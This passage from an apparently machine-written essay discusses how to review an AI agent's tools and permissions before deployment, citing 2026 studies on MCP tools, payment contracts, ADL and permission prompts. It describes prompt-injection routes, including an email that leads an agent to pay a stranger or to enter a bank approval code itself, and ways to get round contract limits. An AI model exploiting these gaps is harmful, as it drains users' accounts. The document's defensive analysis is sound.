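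| Inbox and transfer | A stranger's email makes the agent pay the stranger | Visible (`Untrusted`, `Bank.pay`) | A person has to infer it |
| Inbox and sending email | Private mail goes to a stranger | Visible (`Private`, `Mail.send`) | A person has to infer it |
| Transfer and sending email | Account details from a receipt go to a stranger | Visible (`Private`, `Mail.send`) | Hidden, since nothing describes the receipt |
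| Transfer, many times | Small payments empty the account | Hidden | Hidden |
| Inbox and transfer, if the bank emails approval codes | The agent approves its own payment | Hidden | Hidden |

Anyone who knows about prompt injection could spot the first two dangers from the tools' names. Types matter more in larger environments. Forty tools form 780 pairs, and a program can apply both rules to all of them at once if somebody has declared the labels. JSON could carry these labels too, if MCP adopted the proposed annotations for trust and sensitivity.

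The last row is the most worrying, because every signature is accurate. Suppose the bank emails the customer a code to confirm each large transfer. The agent can read the code in the inbox and enter it, so the customer no longer has to confirm the transfer. A reviewer will notice this only if they know how the bank delivers its codes.

The task needs one bill and one payment. The reviewer can therefore remove `send_email` and ask for narrower versions of the other two tools:

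```
read_bill   : () → Private Untrusted Bill  ! {Mail.read}
pay_plumber : USD → Private Receipt        ! {Bank.pay}
```

`read_bill` returns only emails from the plumber's address. `pay_plumber` makes a single payment of at most $500 from ACC1001 to ACC2002, and the server or a gateway enforces those limits. The environment must still combine untrusted text with a payment, because the user wants the agent to act on an email. But at worst, a forged bill now sends $500 to the plumber, whereas before the review a stranger could have emptied the account.

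### Gaps in the published payment contract

Marron's contract for `transfer` gives a reviewer much more information than a signature does. It limits the amount, requires the user's approval above the limit and names the account the tool may use. A reviewer who reads it closely will still find several gaps.

The limit applies to each payment separately. With a $100 limit, an agent could make 50 payments of $100 and spend $5,000 without asking anybody.

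An approval also remains valid after the payment because it stays in the event log, so one approval of $340 for the plumber covers a second payment too. In the June 2026 paper, Marron concedes the double payment in a footnote that calls the specification "still incomplete", although a caption calls it complete.

The approval specifies the payee and the amount but not the payer. If the user's token covers a household account and a business account, approving a payment from one also permits it from the other. The `permissions` line doesn't fix the payer either, because it builds the permitted address from the `payer` argument, which the caller supplies. The tool may therefore use whichever account the agent names. A reviewer can tell that each call touches one account, but only the token limits which account that can be.

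Without a postcondition, the contract also can't catch a faulty tool that takes $3,400 when asked for $340, or one that debits the payer and pays nobody.

The text around a contract can also mislead a reviewer. The slip in Marron's February 2026 paper about whose account the tool may use implies that the tool can't move money from the payer's account, and so couldn't make payments at all. The paper also calls the approval event `Approve` in the contract but `Approval` in the checker's sample reply. If a real contract and the program that records approvals disagreed like this, every payment above the limit would fail, which is a safe error.

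Two more conditions would close the biggest gaps. With *H* for the event log, they are:

paid today(*H*) + amount ≤ daily limit

approvals(*H*) > payments(*H*)

The second condition applies only above the single-payment limit, and counts the log entries for this payer, payee and amount. Before the first payment to the plumber the counts are 1 and 0, so the call goes ahead. Before the second payment they are 1 and 1, so the call fails. Marron's language could express both conditions. The contract is an illustration rather than production code, but an expert wrote it to make a dangerous interface safe. A less experienced reviewer would probably find it harder to notice a missing condition than to check one that is there.

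### When one tool can do almost anything

A review can produce a useful limit only if the tools are limited. For *How are AI agents used?*, Stein (2026) collected 177,436 tools from 19,388 public MCP servers created between November 2024 and February 2026 and used a language model to classify them in two ways.

Tools can be classified by their impact. Perception tools read data, reasoning tools analyse it, and action tools change something outside the agent. Tools can also be classified by their generality. A narrow tool works in a constrained setting, such as one company's payment service, while a general-purpose tool gives the agent access to an unconstrained one, such as the web through a browser or a computer that runs any code.

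| Kind of tool | Share of published tools | Share of downloads |
|---|---|---|
| Perception | 50.6% | 31.7% |
| Reasoning | 13.4% | 3.3% |
| Action | 36.0% | 64.8% |
| General-purpose (any impact) | 14.3% | 45.4% |

Action tools rose from 27% to 65% of downloads over the 16 months, and general-purpose tools rose from 41% to 50%. The two trends are connected, since 94% of general-purpose server downloads involved action tools. The number of servers that can make payments grew from 47 in January 2025 to 1,578 in February 2026.

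The download figures are a rough measure of how much the tools are used. They cover only 3,854 of the servers, count installations instead of calls, and treat each installation as one use of every tool on the server. The generality labels are also rough, partly because all the tools on a server share one label. Human experts agreed with the model on only 72% of the generality labels, which is fair agreement at best after allowing for chance, compared with 81% of the impact labels.

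Even so, general-purpose tools are common enough to be a serious problem for reviewers. Like a shell, a browser can bypass the limits on an agent's other tools. If the browser is logged in to the bank, the agent can pay anyone through the bank's website, despite the $500 cap on `pay_plumber`. Comparing the environment with the task no longer helps much, because a browser can do nearly any task and nearly any harm. Stein contrasts browsers with a tool that transfers cryptocurrency, whose risks are clear. A browser can download a file the user needs or a piece of malware, and Stein expects that reviewing such calls one by one will become "arduous".

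The reviewer has to check what surrounds the tool as well as its description, such as the browser's logins, the sites it may visit and the files it can open. A fresh browser profile with no saved passwords would restore the $500 cap. Users don't always get such controls. Michael and Roesner (2026), in *How Agents Ask for Permission*, tested five commercial agents in May and June 2026. One of them, ChatGPT's agent mode, works through a remote browser, and they found no way to set permissions for it.

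### A declaration for the whole agent

MCP describes tools one at a time, so a reviewer has to assemble the environment from separate pieces. Nederveld (2026), in *Agent Definition Language (ADL)*, proposes a single JSON document that covers the agent's tools, permissions, data and runtime settings. For the original three tools, it could look like this:

```json
{
  "adl_spec": "0.1.0",
  "name": "Bill payer",
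  "description": "Finds the plumber's bill and pays it.",
  "version": "1.0.0",
  "data_classification": {
    "sensitivity": "confidential",
    "categories": ["financial", "pii"]
  },
  "tools": [
    {
      "name": "read_inbox",
      "description": "Return the user's latest emails.",
      "read_only": true
    },
    {
      "name": "transfer",
      "description": "Transfer an amount from payer to payee.",
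      "requires_confirmation": true
    },
    {
      "name": "send_email",
      "description": "Send an email."
    }
  ],
  "permissions": {
    "network": {
      "allowed_hosts": ["mail.example.com", "bank.example.com"]
    }
  }
}
```

The agent can do only what the document grants, which is the document's most useful feature for a reviewer. This document has no `filesystem` or `execution` section, so the agent can't open files or run commands. The runtime must ask the user before every call to `transfer`. If a document allowed all network hosts with the wildcard `*`, the runtime would have to warn about it, and the draft recommends that a person review such a document before deployment. A runtime that can't enforce a permission must also warn the user, and should refuse to run the agent unless the user accepts the risk.

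The document still doesn't reveal the dangerous combinations. The agent may contact only two hosts, but it can send the user's private emails to anyone through the mail server. The classification marks the data as confidential but doesn't limit who may receive it. The core format has no label for untrusted text and no permission for spending money, so a payment limit would have to go into a tool's argument schema or an extension field that other software may ignore. Nederveld also wants the agent's `description` to be good enough that users needn't examine the tools, which is convenient but encourages them to rely on the part that no program checks.

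In the March draft, Nederveld compares the document to a passport, which should contain everything a gateway or a human operator needs to decide about trust. An author can sign the document, and the February draft recommends that organisations keep a list of approved documents with their digests. A digest is a short fingerprint calculated from a file, so any later change to the file produces a mismatch. This is a good way to check that a document is still the reviewed version, but it doesn't detect changes to the software, because a company can change the program behind `transfer` on its own servers while the document stays the same.

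ADL is one developer's proposal and not an adopted standard. According to IETF (2026), the March draft was due to expire on 19 September 2026.

### How people read permissions

Android phones used to rely on a similar review, in which users saw a list of the permissions an app requested before they installed it. In *Android Permissions*, Felt and colleagues (2012) surveyed 308 users online and observed 25 in a laboratory. In both groups, 17% paid attention to the permissions during installation. Only 3% of the online group correctly answered all three questions about what permissions meant. A notable minority read the warnings and understood them reasonably well, so the lists had some value, but they didn't help most users decide.

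Salerno, Gao and colleagues (2026), in *Let the Agent Do It?*, interviewed 18 software practitioners who use AI agents and surveyed 115 about the permission requests agents make while working. About 48% believed they read the requests carefully, 34% skimmed them and 21% approved them by default. A third had become less careful over time. The true figures may be worse, since people tend to overrate their own care, and the paper cites a report that Claude Code users approve 93% of its requests. One interviewee complained of having to click something "every 10 seconds".

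The same practitioners seem to know what to look for. In the survey, 77% looked more closely at requests to write, delete or gain extra privileges, and 67% were less willing to grant a request that didn't fit the task. Nearly all were more comfortable with read-only access. Someone reviewing an environment before it runs would check the same things, and effect types would show them much of that information.

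*Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026) comes closest to testing decisions made in advance. The 113 participants, none from the software industry, supervised an agent through a simulated day of 18 actions. Seven of the actions went beyond what the user had asked for, such as buying a $25 lounge pass or reading private messages. One group was asked to approve each action, and a second saw only the actions that a model referred to them. The third group set rules beforehand for spending money, sending information, deleting things and reading private data, choosing "allow", "ask" or "never" for each.

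| | Approve every action | Model reviews first | Rules set in advance |
|---|---|---|---|
| Participants | 34 | 44 | 35 |
| Unrequested actions blocked | 59.6% | 53.9% | 39.6% |
| Unrequested actions approved when the agent asked | 40.3% | 46.1% | 66.8% |
| Average number of prompts | 18.0 | 10.0 | 10.9 |

The group with rules blocked the least, mainly because its members avoided deciding in advance. They chose "ask" for 114 of their 140 rules, and when the questions came up during the day, they approved two thirds of the unrequested actions. That rate was high partly because the 16 "never" rules had already blocked 31 actions that would otherwise have produced a prompt. But this selection effect can't explain why the group blocked less overall.

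Yan's result is only indirect evidence about pre-run review, because the participants chose rules for four broad categories and never read a tool description or removed a tool. They weren't risking their own money, and most of the unrequested actions were fairly mild. Yan also added people to the rules group after the original random assignment, which makes the comparison less reliable. Still, the study suggests that many people will put off a question even when they have the chance to settle it beforehand.

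Little is known about how well people read formal notation. In *SpecSyn* (2026), 17 graduate students trained in a contract notation rated machine-written formal specifications about as highly as the reference versions for how well they explained programs. The study did not test whether the students could find mistakes. In *UOOR* (2025), 26% of participants in a small study found software contracts hard to understand and use, while 43% had a positive experience.

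*Modern Software Engineering with Verification Agents* (2026) acknowledges that nobody has measured whether its notation is easier for people to read than Lean. It describes a planned comparison of five specifications written in both notations, with a third version in ordinary mathematical notation to separate readability from familiarity. None of these studies has readers look for a dangerous combination of tools, so it is plausible but untested that typed signatures would help people find one.

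### What to leave to a program

People and programs find different mistakes. *AuXSpec* (2026) checked 300 formal specification problems, each with a reference solution, and confirmed errors in 22. Human reviewers found 21, and an attempted proof exposed the other. In 14 problems the error was in the specification itself, and review and proving overlapped on only three of these. Using both methods is therefore worthwhile, even for specifications that experts have prepared carefully.

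For an agent's environment, a sensible division of the work would be:

| Question | Who should check | Why |
|---|---|---|
| Does the task need this tool? | A person | The task is in the user's own words |
| Is the worst outcome acceptable? | A person | It depends on what the user can afford to lose |
| Do untrusted text and payments occur together? | A program, before the run | There may be hundreds of pairs |
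| Has anything changed since the review? | A program, at every start | Comparing digests is quick and exact |
| Do repeated payments exceed a total? | A program, during the run | The amounts don't exist beforehand |
| Does the tool do more than it declares? | A sandbox or the bank | An accurate and a false description can look the same |

Programs will have to do more of this checking as the number of tools grows. Stein found signs of AI assistance in 62% of MCP servers created in February 2026, up from 6% of those created in January 2025, so the supply of new tools may no longer depend on how fast people can write them.

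A program has to know the tools' effects before it can pool them. Yan tested whether a language model could infer these effects from ordinary names, descriptions and JSON Schemas. Three people had labelled 120 tools from the same information and mostly agreed, so an attentive reader can usually tell from JSON what a single tool does. The model did less well, and when Yan simulated "never" rules, it failed to stop 14% of the tools that the rules should have blocked. If such errors were independent, an environment with five forbidden tools would have a 53% chance (1 − 0.86⁵) of letting at least one through. The set included many deliberately difficult tools, so the rate for ordinary ones is probably lower, but it is still too high for a bank. Declaring each tool's effects would remove the need to infer them, although the declarations could be false.

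A program could also use the declared effects to write the summary the person needs. For the original three tools, the summary might be: "This agent can read all your email, send any of it to anyone, and pay any amount from any account that its token covers." A user could judge that sentence without reading a schema or a type.

Somebody then has to turn the user's answer into limits. Of the 21 permission systems that Michael and Roesner surveyed, 12 try to spare users effort, 11 have formally grounded rules and 12 enforce their rules without relying on a model's judgement, but none fully achieves all three. A reviewer who doubts that the agent needs a tool does better to remove it than to have the agent ask later. In Yan's experiment, the "never" rules stopped every unrequested action they covered, while participants approved 133 of the 199 unrequested actions they were asked about.
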